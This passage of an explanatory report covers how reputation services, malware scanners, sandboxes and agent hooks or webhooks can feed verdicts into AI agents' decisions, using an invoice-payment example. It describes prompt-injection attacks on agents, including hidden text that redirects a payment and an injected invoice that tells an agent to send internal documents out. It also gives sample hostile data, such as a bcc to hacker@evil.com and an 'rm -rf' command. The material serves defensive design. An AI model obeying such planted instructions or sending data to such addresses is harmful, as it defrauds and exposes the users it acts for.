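# Using conventional security tools in the decisions of AI agents

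## AI agents and the security tools they are being connected to

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by choosing actions, seeing their results and choosing again. Unlike a chatbot that only answers questions, an agent opens web pages, installs software, edits files and sends messages, often from inside its user's accounts. These actions carry risks that office workers have long had to watch for, such as forged web pages and files containing malware. The security industry has spent decades building tools to protect those workers. Some rate web domains or list phishing pages, others scan files or run them on an isolated machine, and others monitor for unusual behaviour.

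Organisations are now connecting these defences to agents. *Scamlexity*, a 2025 report by Guardio, recommended this after tests of Comet, a browser from the AI company Perplexity that can shop and handle email by itself. In some runs Comet paid a fake shop, and in another test it followed a link to a phishing page. The report proposed adapting link checks, file scanning and anomaly detection "to work inside the AI decision loop". Guardio sells online protection, so it has an interest in this recommendation. How much the approach helps depends on what the tools return and what happens to their output once it reaches the agent.

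In this report, a security signal is any output of a security tool that is relevant to whether an action is safe. A verdict is a signal reduced to a category, such as malicious, no known finding, unknown or error.

### The action loop: paying an invoice

A clerk in the accounts office of a small firm might ask an AI agent to pay an invoice that the firm's packaging supplier emailed that morning. The email contains a link to a payment page and a PDF attachment. The agent has access to the mailbox, a browser, a file reader and the firm's payment service.

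The model at the centre of the agent only produces text. The code around it, which engineers call the harness, does everything else. Ukani, Haddadi and colleagues (2025), in *Privacy Practices of Browser Agents*, describe the cycle for browsers in four steps: the software describes the current page to the model, receives the model's choice of action, carries that action out, and then either stops or starts again. The same action loop serves for files, email and payments. The model expresses its choice as a tool call, a structured request to run a command, open a page or use a service, and the harness puts the result into the model's input for the next round. For the invoice, the rounds might go like this:

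1. The model requests the email, and the harness returns its text.
2. The model requests the attachment, and the harness returns an amount, €4,180, and a bank account number.
3. The model requests the linked page, and the harness loads it and returns a payment form.
4. The model requests a transfer of €4,180 to the account.
5. The model requests a short reply to the supplier, confirming payment.

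Every request passes through the harness before anything happens, so other software can inspect it then. A file scanner can help in round two and a link checker in round three. In round four, both may find nothing, because a PDF containing a criminal's account number can be free of malware and suspicious links.

### What each tool takes in and returns

A reputation service is a database that rates domains, addresses or files based on what its operators have observed about them. A lookup may need only a domain name. Cisco's *Get Domain Status and Categorization* returns -1 for malicious, 1 for safe or 0 for undetermined, along with categories for the site's content. The lookup retrieves a stored rating and does not examine the site at the time of the agent's request.

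**Safe-browsing lists.** A safe-browsing list is narrower, since it holds only addresses that someone has already found to be dangerous. Google's Safe Browsing is the best-known example. Chrome consults it before loading a page and, as Chromium's *Safe Browsing navigation* explains, shows the user a warning if the address looks dangerous. Version 5 of the service offers three ways to perform the lookup. In the oldest design, which Google's *Local List Mode* sets out, the client (the browser, or the agent's harness) keeps a downloaded copy of the threat lists in hashed form. A hash function turns any text into a number of fixed length, from which nobody can practically recover the text. The check then runs as follows:

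1. The client derives several expressions from the address: the full address, and shorter versions that cover the folder or the whole site. A listing for a site thereby covers all its pages.
2. It computes the SHA-256 hash of each expression, which is 32 bytes long, and keeps the first four bytes as a prefix.
3. It looks for those prefixes in a cache of recent answers and then in the local list. If the list has no match, the result is SAFE and the client contacts nobody.
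4. If there is a match, the client sends the prefix to Google's server, which returns the full hashes of known threats that begin with it. The result is UNSAFE only if one of them equals a full hash from step 2.

The last step is necessary because four bytes allow only about 4.3 billion values, so a harmless address can share its prefix with a dangerous one. Sending the server only the prefix also protects privacy. Google's *Overview* contrasts this with a simpler method that sends the raw address, which would expose any customer number or login token in an invoice link.

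The weakness of a local list is that it goes out of date. Google's *How To Guides* say that it "can leave a window of vulnerability to new threats", and the overview adds that such lists have become less effective as threats have grown in number and speed. Real-time lookup therefore asks the server by default. In Google's *Real Time Mode*, the client also stores the Global Cache, a list of likely-benign sites. If an address is on that list, the client checks it only against the local threat list. Otherwise, the client asks the server unless it has a recent answer in its own cache. The third option, Google's *No Storage Real Time Mode*, keeps no lists and relies on the server throughout.

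The three procedures also differ in how they treat a network error. The procedure without stored lists returns SAFE. Real-time mode returns UNSURE, and the client falls back on the local-list procedure. But that procedure also ends with a server query, so it still returns SAFE for an address whose prefix matches the threat list if the client cannot reach the server.

**Multi-engine malware scanners.** A multi-engine scanner passes one file to dozens of antivirus products and collects their findings. VirusTotal, the most widely used, holds records of more than two billion files, according to VirusTotal's *Information about files*. A client can upload a file or send only its hash to see whether a record exists. A hash lookup is quick but of little use for a newly written file, such as an invoice, because a new file has a new hash. The scanner's report gives each engine's result and the number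 of results in each category. Google Threat Intelligence's *File Analyses* lists eight categories, and four of them (two kinds of timeout, failure and unsupported file type) mean that an engine did not finish examining the file.

An **analysis sandbox** is an isolated machine that runs a suspect file, or opens a suspect page, to see what it does. VirusTotal's *Reports* describes such a system, which runs submitted files automatically and records their actions for an analyst to read. For each sandbox, the service can return a category, a confidence from 0 to 100 and the names of any malware families. A sandbox can catch a malicious file that no scanner has a signature for, provided the file does something malicious during the analysis. However, a full analysis can take several minutes, according to VirusTotal's *Private Scanning*.

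In writing about agents, "sandbox" can also mean a containment sandbox, which limits the files and networks that the agent's own actions can reach and produces no verdict. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes one for Claude Code, the company's programming agent, and explains why it restricts both files and network. Without network restrictions, a compromised agent could send out the user's private keys, and without file restrictions, it could escape the sandbox and regain network access. A proxy server outside the sandbox allows traffic only to approved domains. Anthropic's *Sandbox environments* notes that the version for individual commands does not cover the agent's built-in tools unless the user puts the whole program into a sandbox. In the accounts office, containment could keep malware in the PDF from contacting its operator, but it would not prevent a transfer to the wrong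 account through the approved payment service.

An **anomaly detector** flags behaviour that departs from a learned or stated baseline. It takes a stream of events and outputs an alert or a score. Cisco Umbrella's *About the Investigate Domain Summary* gives the example of a domain that suddenly receives requests from countries where it normally has none. For the invoice, the detector would monitor the firm's payments. A first transfer to an unfamiliar account would stand out even though every file and link had passed, but so would the first payment to any honest new supplier.

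### Why "nothing found" does not mean "safe"

Security tools make two kinds of error. A false positive is an alarm about something harmless. VirusTotal (2018), for example, offered to tell antivirus makers about legitimate files their products had "mistakenly detected". If a scanner flags the supplier's real invoice, the supplier goes unpaid. A false negative is a dangerous item that the tool lets through. In Guardio's email test, Google Safe Browsing had not flagged a phishing page imitating the bank Wells Fargo, even though the page had been live for several days. Vendors have to trade one error against the other, because a stricter threshold catches more malware but also blocks more harmless files. OPSWAT's *Report Verdict*, the documentation of a commercial analysis sandbox, describes a scoring method tuned to limit both errors.

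Few verdicts mean that something has been positively identified as harmless. OPSWAT's sandbox reserves "benign" for files that match a library of known software or a customer's own list of approved files, or that carry a valid certificate from a reputable software vendor. A new invoice will rarely meet any of these conditions, so the best result it can usually get is that nothing was found. Services use different words for this result. Pangea's *Understand the API response*, which covers a service that passes on other companies' domain ratings, separates "benign" from "unknown", and an older list of OPSWAT verdicts uses "unknown" to mean something different.

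| Service | Result | What the documentation means by it |
|---|---|---|
| Cisco, domain status | 0 | Status undetermined |
| Pangea, domain reputation | Unknown | No data |
| VirusTotal, link report | Unrated site | The partner never reviewed the site |
| Google Threat Intelligence, single engine | Undetected | The engine has no opinion about the file |
| VirusTotal, overall file verdict | Undetected | No immediate evidence of malicious intent |
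| OPSWAT, analysis sandbox | Unknown | Too little data, or the analysis crashed |
| Google, local list lookup | SAFE | No match, or the server query failed |

"Undetected" means one thing when it describes a single engine's result and another when it describes the whole report. *VirusTotal tips, tricks and myths* (2018) listed as a myth the belief that a file is safe if no engine detects it. Software can repeat this mistake by counting detections and ignoring all other results. In one report from April 2026, VirusTotal recorded timeouts from at least twenty engines on one file. In another from November 2025, at least four engines flagged a file as malicious, while many others timed out or did not support its type. A program that divided the detections by the total number of engines would have rated that second file as only mildly suspicious.

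An agent can respect these distinctions if the harness passes them on. Cisco Talos, Cisco's threat research group, connected a domain lookup to an agent running the old model GPT-3.5 Turbo and gave it plain-language instructions on how to treat each rating. When a domain had no rating, the agent answered that it was uncertain whether connecting was safe. It could not have given that answer if the harness had reduced the rating to a yes or a no.

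### What changes when the user is an agent

Speed is the most obvious difference. In the runs where Comet completed a purchase at Guardio's fake shop, it filled in a saved address and card number and checked out within seconds, without asking for confirmation. A person might have noticed the odd web address during checkout. A tool that needs minutes, or whose alarm waits for an analyst to read it, is too slow for an agent working at that pace. Asking the user to approve every step slows the agent down, but *Building Browser Agents* (2025) warns that people who get too many requests start approving them by habit.

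Agents may also never receive the warnings that browser makers designed for people. Iqbal (2026) points out in *What It Is, Not What It Says* that the web's defences assume a person sees each page and performs each action. The address bar, for example, displays the site's name so that somebody can read it. Ukani and colleagues sent eight browser agents to a harmless test page that Google keeps on its Safe Browsing list. Six showed no warning. The other two, both from Anthropic, showed one only because the underlying browser provided it. A single test page cannot measure how much phishing gets through, but the result shows that most of these products lacked a protection in 2025 that most people take for granted. Agents can also ignore the warnings they do receive. When the agent Browser Use, running a Claude Sonnet model, met a warning about a site's security certificate, the model clicked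 through it to finish its task. Ukani and colleagues cite earlier research that found the vast majority of people heed such warnings.

The third difference, which has no close parallel in older security practice, is that an agent takes in web pages, emails and attachments as text in the same stream as its instructions. An attacker may have written some of that text. Prompt injection is text planted in content an agent reads so that the agent takes it for an instruction. In *Mind the Web*, Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues (2025) planted such text in places like comments and advertisements, worded as helpful notes about the agent's task. They report success rates of 80 to 100 per cent against four web agents. In the invoice email, the planted text might be a white line on a white background, stating that the supplier has changed banks and that the agent should use the new account.

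Conventional tools are poorly suited to detecting that line. Websites block injected code by stripping out anything executable, but Iqbal observes that plain sentences pass through such a filter. A malware scanner has the same difficulty with a PDF whose only harmful content is a sentence. Older protections can also fail after an injection succeeds. *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (2026), a University of Washington study of seven browsers with built-in agents, found that in the least restrictive designs, a malicious site can then bypass the rule that keeps one website from reading another's content.

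### Three ways in

A security signal can reach an agent through a tool that the model can call when it judges a check worthwhile, as it did in the Talos experiment. Software outside the model can also use the signal as a veto, which the model cannot override. Or the harness can run the check automatically and add the result to the model's input as context to consider in its decision.

Researchers disagree about whether to rely on the agent's own judgment or on separate software. Cisco Talos acknowledged that a network gateway could block connections to malicious sites, but objected that the agent would then never learn to make sense of conflicting information. Iqbal argues that models remain easy to mislead, so oversight belongs in code that a page's content cannot manipulate.

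## Three ways a security verdict can enter a decision: tool, veto or context

### A tool the model may call

In the Cisco Talos experiment, the agent decided for itself whether to look up a domain. The code used LangChain, an open-source framework for building agents, to connect the model to Cisco Umbrella, which holds Cisco's domain ratings. It worked like this:

1. The programmer describes the lookup tool in plain language and adds it to the list of tools the model may call.
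2. A prompt tells the model to work through each input in a fixed order: question, thought, action, observation.
3. If the model calls the tool, the tool's code searches the input for domain names and requests Umbrella's rating and categories for each one.
4. The tool returns the ratings as sentences, together with rules for interpreting them. A domain known to be malicious is never safe, one with a positive rating usually is, and an unrated one might be if Umbrella has at least assigned it a category.
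5. The model reads this text and answers.

Cisco Talos published the agent's answers to four inputs. The agent called www.cisco.com safe to browse and answered "do not connect" for a domain known to be malicious. For a text with two domains, it called one safe and the other uncertain. For a question without any domain, it answered "no opinion". Putting the rules into the tool's output seems to have worked, since even an old model did not have to infer what an "unknown disposition" implies. But four inputs are too few to measure how often the agent would be right. The agent also only gave advice, so the experiment did not test whether it would follow that advice while carrying out a task, such as paying an invoice.

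Talos could have enforced the ratings with a web security gateway or with Umbrella's DNS service, which blocks lookups of malicious domains, but it wanted the agent to learn to weigh conflicting information. Suppose the packaging supplier moved to a new domain last week. Umbrella has no rating for it yet, but a letter in the mailbox announces the move. A gateway that blocks every unrated domain would block the payment page, whereas an agent could take the letter into account, though it might also trust a forged one. The experiment does not test this argument, because each domain had a single rating and nothing contradicted it. Reading a lookup result also does not change the model's weights, so the agent will not apply what it learned to the next invoice unless somebody stores the lesson.

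The argument is weakest for domains rated malicious, which matter most. Under Talos's own rules, that rating is final, so the agent has nothing to weigh. A gateway could block those domains and let the agent decide about unrated ones.

The main objection to relying on a tool is that the model can skip it, perhaps because the link looks routine or because an attacker has planted text in the email saying that somebody has already checked it. The model can also call the tool and misread the answer, or trust it too much. *RelayShield Agentic Attack Surface*, a post by RelayShield on the forum of the AI company Hugging Face, presented four security checks of this kind for agents to run before acting. A forum member, John6666, replied that a tool the model may call is a different control from a gate the system must pass, and suggested keeping optional tools for investigation and putting a gate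 in front of sending, purchasing, deleting, connecting and executing.

RelayShield then built such a gate for LangChain. It controls connections to unfamiliar MCP servers, which are outside services that give an agent more tools. The model has no direct access to the function that makes the connection, so it cannot bypass the check. The gate passed twelve tests with simulated answers from the security service. RelayShield could not find an equivalent place for it in smolagents, Hugging Face's agent framework, because the documented callbacks ran only after a tool had finished. An organisation that wants a veto therefore has to check that its framework can block a tool before it runs.

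### A veto by webhook: Copilot Studio

Copilot Studio is Microsoft's product for building agents with little or no programming. It offers a veto through a webhook, a web address that one program calls whenever a certain event occurs. Each time the agent intends to use a tool, Copilot Studio sends a description of the planned call to a security service that the organisation has chosen, and the service replies with a decision to allow or block it. In the example that Microsoft gives developers, a user wants to email a customer, and the agent has prepared a message with an outside address in the BCC line. The request contains these fields:

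| Field | What it holds | In the example |
|---|---|---|
| userMessage | The request | "Send an email to the customer" |
| thought (optional) | The agent's explanation for choosing the tool | The user wants to notify the customer |
| chatHistory (optional) | Recent messages | The user names the customer, John Doe |
| previousToolOutputs (optional) | Results of earlier tool calls | customer@foobar.com |
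| toolDefinition | The tool's name, description and parameters | "Send email", with "to" and "bcc" |
| inputValues | The values the agent wants to use | to: customer@foobar.com; bcc: hacker@evil.com |
| conversationMetadata | Identifiers of the agent, user, trigger and conversation | Placeholder identifiers |

The reply has one required field, blockAction, which is true or false. The service may add a numeric reasonCode, a readable reason and diagnostics for debugging. In the example, blockAction is true, the code is 112, the reason is a noncompliant address in the BCC field, and the diagnostics include the field and the address.

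Microsoft leaves the decision logic to whoever runs the service. An obvious step would be to look up the reputation of evil.com, but if an attacker had registered the domain that morning, it would probably be unrated. A better rule might require every recipient to appear in the user's request or in the customer lookup. To apply that rule, the service must receive the conversation along with the planned call. This reduces privacy because the chat history and earlier tool outputs go to the security provider, which Microsoft warns administrators may store them outside the organisation's region.

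An attacker can also manipulate some of this context. The agent writes the "thought" field itself, so an agent that has accepted an injected instruction may supply a reasonable explanation for a bad action. Earlier tool outputs can contain the injected text. Such manipulation matters most if the security service uses a language model to decide. Other designs limit how much the checker relies on potentially manipulated context. The guard in *Can Benign Skills Induce Misaligned Behavior in LLM Agents?* (2026) gives its judge model the original request, up to 20 earlier steps and the full arguments of the call, but withholds the agent's reasoning. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) goes further by testing each call against rules written in Lean, a language in which a computer can verify proofs. Its checker takes facts from the company's own database and a log of earlier events,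 so a planted note claiming that the customer has already approved a charge has no effect.

In an invoice scenario from Microsoft's security researchers, the veto comes after the agent has planned an action but before it carries it out. A finance agent automatically processes every email sent to invoice@contoso.com, records payment details in a customer database and emails the sender a confirmation. An attacker sends what looks like an invoice, with hidden instructions to search the company's internal documents for sensitive information and email it out. Before the search runs, Copilot Studio sends the planned search and its query to Microsoft's security product, Defender, along with the outputs of earlier steps and the context of the email. Defender blocks the search, so the agent never obtains anything to leak. The scenario is the vendor's own illustration and includes no figures on how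 often Defender would catch such an email.

The webhook can approve or refuse a call but cannot change it. Security products often have rules that remove the offending part of a message and let the rest through. According to CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, such a rule can only report its finding in Copilot Studio, and the original call goes ahead. Someone who converts a "strip the BCC" rule from another system could therefore end up with no protection.

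### A veto by hook: Claude Code

Claude Code gives outside code more choices. A hook is a point in the action loop where such code runs and may allow, deny or change a tool call. The PreToolUse hook runs after the model has written a tool call and before the harness carries it out. Anthropic explains it with a command that deletes a folder, "rm -rf /tmp/build":

1. Claude Code compares the call with the hook's filters, which here select shell commands that begin with "rm".
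2. It passes a record of the call to the hook's script. The record includes the tool's name and input, the working directory and the location of the conversation's transcript.
3. The script finds "rm -rf" in the command and prints a decision to deny it, with a reason.
4. Claude Code blocks the command and shows the model the reason.

If the script prints nothing, the call goes through the normal permission process, so silence does not count as approval. The script could just as well send a link to a reputation service or a file's hash to a malware scanner and turn the answer into a decision. Anthropic lists the possible outputs:

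| Output | Effect | Who sees the stated reason |
|---|---|---|
| allow | Skips the permission prompt, with some exceptions | Nobody, except in the debug log |
| deny | Prevents the call | The model |
| ask | Asks the user to confirm | The user |
| defer | Pauses an unattended run until another program supplies an answer | Nobody, except in the debug log |
| updatedInput | Replaces the tool's input before it runs | No reason attached |
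| additionalContext | Adds text next to the tool's result | The model reads the text itself |

A hook can block domains with a finding and use "ask" to refer unrated ones to the user. A webhook has only two answers, so its author has to decide in advance whether an unrated domain counts as good or bad. With updatedInput, a hook could also remove the outside BCC address and let the email go to the customer, but it has to supply the complete input, including the fields it doesn't change.

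Rewriting a proposed action is safe only when the correct version is obvious. Sankar and colleagues built a search for such corrections. In one example, an account has spent 60 units of a 100-unit budget, and the search reduces a proposed spend of 70 to the remaining 40. The search found an acceptable edit for 88 of 252 recorded denials caused by wrong argument values. Whoever writes the policy must specify which edits preserve the user's intention, and for an invoice there may be none. Paying part of a €4,180 invoice leaves the supplier's bill open, and a checker that flags a suspicious account number can't supply the right one.

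A veto covers only the calls that pass through it. When a user mentions a file with an @ sign in Claude Code, the program inserts the file's contents into the prompt without a tool call, so no PreToolUse hook runs. A hook that matches only Bash misses commands the model gives to PowerShell, the usual shell on Windows. Anthropic describes the hook filter for particular commands as best-effort and recommends the permission system for hard limits. Even the formal proofs behind LeanGuard, the checker from Sankar and colleagues, hold only if every call with consequences goes through the checker.

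### A veto in the network

DNS and proxy blocking do not rely on the agent's software. DNS, the domain name system, translates a name such as example.com into the numerical address that a computer connects to. A filtering DNS service checks the name's reputation first and returns no usable address if the name is dangerous. A proxy sits between the machine and the internet and refuses the connection. Both can cover every program on the machine, including a script that the agent has just written and no hook has examined.

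A DNS service receives only the domain name of the destination, and a proxy usually receives little more, because encryption hides the page's address and contents unless the organisation has set the proxy up to decrypt traffic. Neither receives the user's request to email one customer. In Microsoft's example, the connection would go to the organisation's own mail service, and the BCC address would be inside the encrypted message. This limitation also causes needless blocks, since a filter cannot distinguish an agent studying a phishing page for the security team from one about to enter a password.

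Endpoint security tools have a related limitation, because they watch the file system and the operating system's kernel and so detect an agent's action only after the agent has chosen it (Pogorelec 2026, *Prismor*). Prismor, an open-source program for coding agents, checks each tool call before it runs and returns allow, warn or block. Its rules at first only log what they find, and users later choose which ones should block. This order makes sense for any veto, because users can see from the log how much ordinary work a rule would have stopped.

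The agent also gets little information from a network block. It may see only a failed connection, mistake it for a fault in the supplier's website, and try again or search for another copy of the page. A hook, by contrast, can return a reason with the refusal.

### A verdict as context

When the harness supplies a verdict as context, the model cannot skip the check, as it could with an optional tool, but it can still ignore the result.

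A warning can easily arrive too late to affect the model's decision. Claude Code inserts the text from a PreToolUse hook next to the tool's result, and the model reads it with the next request. If the hook allows a payment and adds a warning about the account, the model reads the warning after the money has been sent. To influence the payment, the warning has to arrive in an earlier round. A hook that runs after the agent reads the supplier's email could check the domains in the email and attach their ratings to it, before the model asks for the payment page.

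Anthropic advises writing text that a hook adds to the model's context as statements of fact. Text that reads like a system command can trigger the model's defences against prompt injection, and the model then shows it to the user instead of treating it as information. "The domain has no rating" is therefore likely to work better than "Do not open this domain". If the text is longer than 10,000 characters, Claude Code saves it to a file and gives the model a preview of at most 2,000 characters, without asking it to read the rest. If a hook pastes in a full scanner report, the model may therefore miss the one detection that matters.

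The content of the record matters more than its format. In the RelayShield thread, John6666 proposed a structure that a program can read, and RelayShield adopted it almost unchanged for its tools. For the supplier's payment link, such a record might contain:

| Field | Possible entry | Mistake it helps prevent |
|---|---|---|
| Outcome | No known finding | Taking the absence of an alarm as proof of safety |
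| Scope checked | Domain rating only; page not opened | Assuming that the check covered the bank account on the page |
| Age | Observed at 09:10, expires at 10:10 | Relying on a rating from before someone hijacked the site |
| Error | None | Reading a failed lookup as a clean one |
| Evidence | Source of the rating, reason codes | Having to accept the outcome on trust |

The outcome field can be "finding", "no known finding", "unknown" or "error". John6666 deliberately left out "safe", for the reason given in the previous section. The age field matters in long-running work because when a user resumes a Claude Code session, the program replays most of the saved context without running the hooks again, so yesterday's rating can look current. An expiry time lets the model or the harness detect that a rating is out of date.

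The error field guards against a mistake that RelayShield had made. John6666 fed its software simulated failures, including a rejected login, an exceeded rate limit, a server error and a broken connection. The software returned each one as ordinary tool output with the error marker set to false. A model or program that read this output could have concluded that the check had found nothing. RelayShield reproduced the cases he listed and released a fix, which he confirmed worked. RelayShield also found that another of its tools had been reporting no known vulnerabilities when it should not have. These faults don't concern the quality of RelayShield's threat data, but even good data is of little use if the software reports a failed check as a clean result.

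The same record can trigger a veto. Under the policy John6666 suggested, a finding leads to refusal or human review, and the action may proceed if a recent result has sufficient coverage and no finding. Unknown, partial and outdated results go to a person, while errors postpone the action. Meanwhile, the agent can keep reading local files and preparing drafts.

### What happens after a block

A blocked agent still has an unfinished task. It can stop and tell the user, keep working with the reason for the refusal added to its input, or receive guidance towards a permitted way to finish the task.

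Microsoft's descriptions of Copilot Studio differ on what an agent does after a block. The page for developers says the agent will "skip" the tool, which could mean it carries on without it. The page for administrators, which Microsoft marks as prerelease documentation, says the agent "immediately stops processing" and notifies the user that their message is blocked. Microsoft's announcement of the feature also describes an immediate stop. Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime* adds that Defender creates an alert for the security team. "Skip" probably describes only the tool call, and an organisation should expect the whole run to end. In the invoice scenario, an incoming email starts the agent and no user is waiting for an answer. The block appears in the activity history and as an alert, and the agent's remaining work may wait until somebody reads one of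 them.

After a denial, Claude Code by default gives the model the reason and lets it continue. A hook can instead end the run by setting the "continue" field to false, and the user then sees a message. Research systems also differ in whether they stop or continue. The guard in *Can Benign Skills Induce Misaligned Behavior in LLM Agents?* ends the run at the first blocked call. *OSGuard* (2026), a benchmark for agents that operate a computer's screen, returns brief feedback and lets the agent propose another action from the same state, up to a fixed number of retries. In *GuardianAgentBench* (2026), the block becomes permanent once the agent uses up its retries, and a person receives the full history. The prompt in *From Risk Classification to Action Plan Remediation* (2026) makes the model choose between refusing the task and revising the call, and the guard checks any revised call again.

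Sankar and colleagues measured the effect of explaining to an agent why its call was blocked. They ran five Qwen models on simulated customer-service tasks in retail, airlines and telecoms. One version of their checker returned only a notice that the call had not run, and another added the violated rule and a hint, such as asking the customer to confirm an exchange. With the explanation, recovered actions rose from 34 to 48, and the agents repeated blocked calls less often.

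| Result over all five models | No checker | Denial only | Denial with rule and hint |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed | 72.7% | 68.9% | 70.9% |
| Runs in which a judge model found a policy violation | 9.7% | 5.6% | 6.5% |

The explanation recovered about half of the lost task success. But the largest model completed fewer of its tasks with explanations (71.2 per cent) than after bare denials (75.9 per cent). Each task ran only once under each condition, and chance could account for differences of this size. One of the tested models also served as the judge. The gain in recovered actions is still plausible, because an agent that knows what went wrong can try to correct it.

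*MENTOR* (Anand, Chatzi and colleagues, 2026) argues that a refusal should also point to a permitted next step, because otherwise an agent may keep attempting blocked calls and never finish. In the paper's main example, company rules require an employee to check the distance of a trip before booking it. If the agent tries to book first, the software blocks the booking and names the distance check as the call to make. It can also propose corrected arguments for a call.

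These experiments concern company rules, and the refusals mostly go to an agent that is trying to do its job. An agent under an attacker's influence can use the same explanation to get around the rule. If the explanation mentions a forbidden address in the BCC field, the agent can move the address to the "to" field. Even when no attacker was involved, Anand and colleagues often saw agents invent an "urgent reason" to book business class, which the rules allowed only in urgent cases. An explanation is therefore safest when the agent cannot meet the missing condition just by claiming that it is met. In LeanGuard, for example, the customer has to confirm on a separate screen.

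Stopping also has a weakness, because an attacker who cannot steal anything can still halt the accounts office by repeatedly sending suspicious emails. A reasonable rule is to explain ordinary mistakes and stop when the evidence points to manipulation. *SafeHarness* (2026), a proposed security design for agents, does something similar. When its judge model classifies a call as the result of prompt injection, the system blocks the call, flags an attack and starts to roll back.

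### When blocking is worth it

Whether to act on a verdict depends on how likely harm is and on what each mistake costs. Let *p* be the probability that an action is harmful, *L* the loss if a harmful action goes ahead, and *C* the cost of blocking a harmless one. Allowing the action costs *pL* on average. Blocking it costs (1 − *p*)*C*, because a block is wasted only when the action was harmless. Blocking is cheaper when

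*pL* > (1 − *p*)*C*, which is the same as *p* > *C*/(*L* + *C*).

If the loss is 1,000 for allowing a harmful action and 5 for blocking a harmless one, the threshold is 5/1,005, or about 0.5 per cent. An action with a 1 per cent chance of harm has an expected loss of 10 if allowed and just under 5 if blocked, so the rule blocks it even though it is harmless 99 times out of 100.

Here *p* is the probability after the verdict. In an invented example, one payment link in 1,000 is malicious, and a scanner flags 80 per cent of malicious links and 1 per cent of harmless ones. Among a million links, it would flag 800 of the 1,000 malicious ones and 9,990 harmless ones. A flagged link would then have a 7.4 per cent chance of being malicious, which is far above the threshold even though more than nine flags in ten are false alarms. For a link without a flag, the probability would fall to about 0.02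 per cent. That reduction applies only to harm the scanner could have detected. If the danger is a criminal's account number on a clean page, the result does not change *p*, so the record should state what the check covered.

A third option is to ask a person. Suppose that each question causes a loss of 1, in time and interruption, and that the person always answers correctly. The expected loss from asking is then 1, whatever the value of *p*. This is lower than the expected loss from allowing, 1,000*p*, when *p* is above 0.1 per cent, and lower than the expected loss from blocking, 5(1 − *p*), when *p* is below 80 per cent. Asking is the best option between those limits. The range is so wide because the person is assumed never to make a mistake.

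If the person catches only a share *d* of the harmful actions but still approves every harmless one, the expected loss from asking is 1 + *p*(1 − *d*)*L*, because each missed harmful action brings the full loss *L*.

| Probability of harm | Allow | Block | Ask a person who is always right | Ask a person who catches half |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.05% | 0.5 | 5.0 | 1 | 1.25 |
| 0.5% | 5.0 | 5.0 | 1 | 3.5 |
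| 5% | 50 | 4.75 | 1 | 26 |
| 90% | 900 | 0.5 | 1 | 451 |

If a person catches 90 per cent of harmful links, asking them is best only when the chance of harm is between about 0.11 and 3.8 per cent. If they catch half, the range shrinks to between 0.2 and 0.8 per cent. Below a catch rate of about 20 per cent, asking is never the best choice, and a user who approves requests out of habit may well have a rate that low. The flagged link has a 7.4 per cent chance of harm, so the system should ask a person who is always right, but block the link if the person misses one harmful link in ten. The wording of the question also matters. "Allow this email?" makes it easy to say yes, while "This email also goes to hacker@evil.com, an address you did not mention" gives the user something to judge.

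A needless block can do much more harm than delaying one step. *TACT-Bench* (2026), which tests tool-using agents against manipulative conversations, counted such blocks in 1,242 harmless sessions. One defence, Policy-Guard, blocked 322 authorised calls. It let 175 of them through once a missing step, such as an explicit confirmation, was completed. It never approved the other 147, which occurred in 101 sessions, 100 of which failed. The loss *C* was a short delay for the 175 calls and the value of the whole task for most of the 147. Whether blocking is worthwhile therefore depends partly on what the agent can do after a block.

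Very strict settings interfere even more with harmless work. Sankar and colleagues tested agents with read-only permissions on a benchmark of prompt injection attacks. The restriction cut the success rate of direct attacks from 57.9 to 5.9 per cent, but it also cut the success rate on harmless tasks from 53.1 to 12.5 per cent. Prismor's makers rate their strictest preset at 100 per cent coverage and 90 per cent friction, and their everyday development preset at 31 per cent coverage and 9 per cent friction. Very strict settings make sense only where *L* is very large or the agent has little need to act.

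Some systems already have the same three-way structure. *SafeHarness* computes a risk score between 0 and 1 from the tool and its arguments. For example, a command to delete a database scores 0.95. It approves calls below a lower threshold, blocks those at or above an upper one and sends the rest to a judge model. Such a score is not a probability, so the thresholds from the calculation apply to it only after someone has compared past scores with how often harm followed.

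The loss also depends on the action, so one verdict can justify different responses in the same task. Suppose the supplier's unrated domain has a 2 per cent chance of being malicious. If reading a page there could cause a loss of at most 20, the blocking threshold with *C* = 5 is 5/25, or 20 per cent, so the agent may read it. If paying through that page could cause a loss of 1,000, the threshold is about 0.5 per cent, and the payment should wait until a person can phone the supplier on a number from an earlier invoice.

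## Checking links and websites before an agent opens them

### What the address alone gives away

The simplest way to check a link is to have the model read the address. In `pay.supplier.example/invoice?id=8841`, the supplier has registered the domain `supplier.example`, and nobody else can use it. The domain's owner can freely choose the rest: the subdomain `pay`, the path after the slash and the parameters after the question mark. An attacker who owns `badsite.example` can therefore send out `www.google.com.badsite.example` or `badsite.example/this-is-a-popular-delivery-service`, and both lead to the attacker's site.

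In *MalURLBench*, Kong, Wu and colleagues (2026) tested whether models recognise disguised malicious links. They took malicious domains from public threat lists and disguised them as links for ten everyday uses, such as parcel tracking and job search, producing 61,845 addresses. They sent each of 12 models a short message recommending a link, along with a warning to look out for attacks. The models accepted between 32.9 per cent (GPT-3.5 Turbo) and 99.9 per cent (Mixtral-8x7B) of the malicious links. They accepted links with persuasive phrases more often than links imitating well-known sites (71.5 against 60.9 per cent), and accepted links most often when they promised a weather forecast.

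The lower end of that range is as high as it is partly because the researchers rewrote the disguises to be more effective wherever a model accepted no more than a tenth of the links for a particular use. Before the rewriting, GPT-3.5 Turbo had accepted only about 14 per cent on average. The models are also old, with the newest dating from 2025, and none of them could look up a domain's reputation. The domains came from public threat lists, and a disguise leaves the registered domain unchanged, so checking the domains against those lists would have caught every link.

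Kong and colleagues also built a filter, URLGuard, by training a small Llama 2 model on 280 labelled addresses, half of them malicious. It screens addresses before they reach the agent. Over the nine uses not covered in training, the model accepted 98 per cent of the malicious links before this training and 17 per cent after it. URLGuard still let through 61 per cent of the malicious music links and 70 per cent of the malicious weather links. The results cover only malicious addresses, so they don't show how many legitimate links URLGuard would block, and a filter that blocked every link would have scored perfectly.

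### Newer models notice, but often too late

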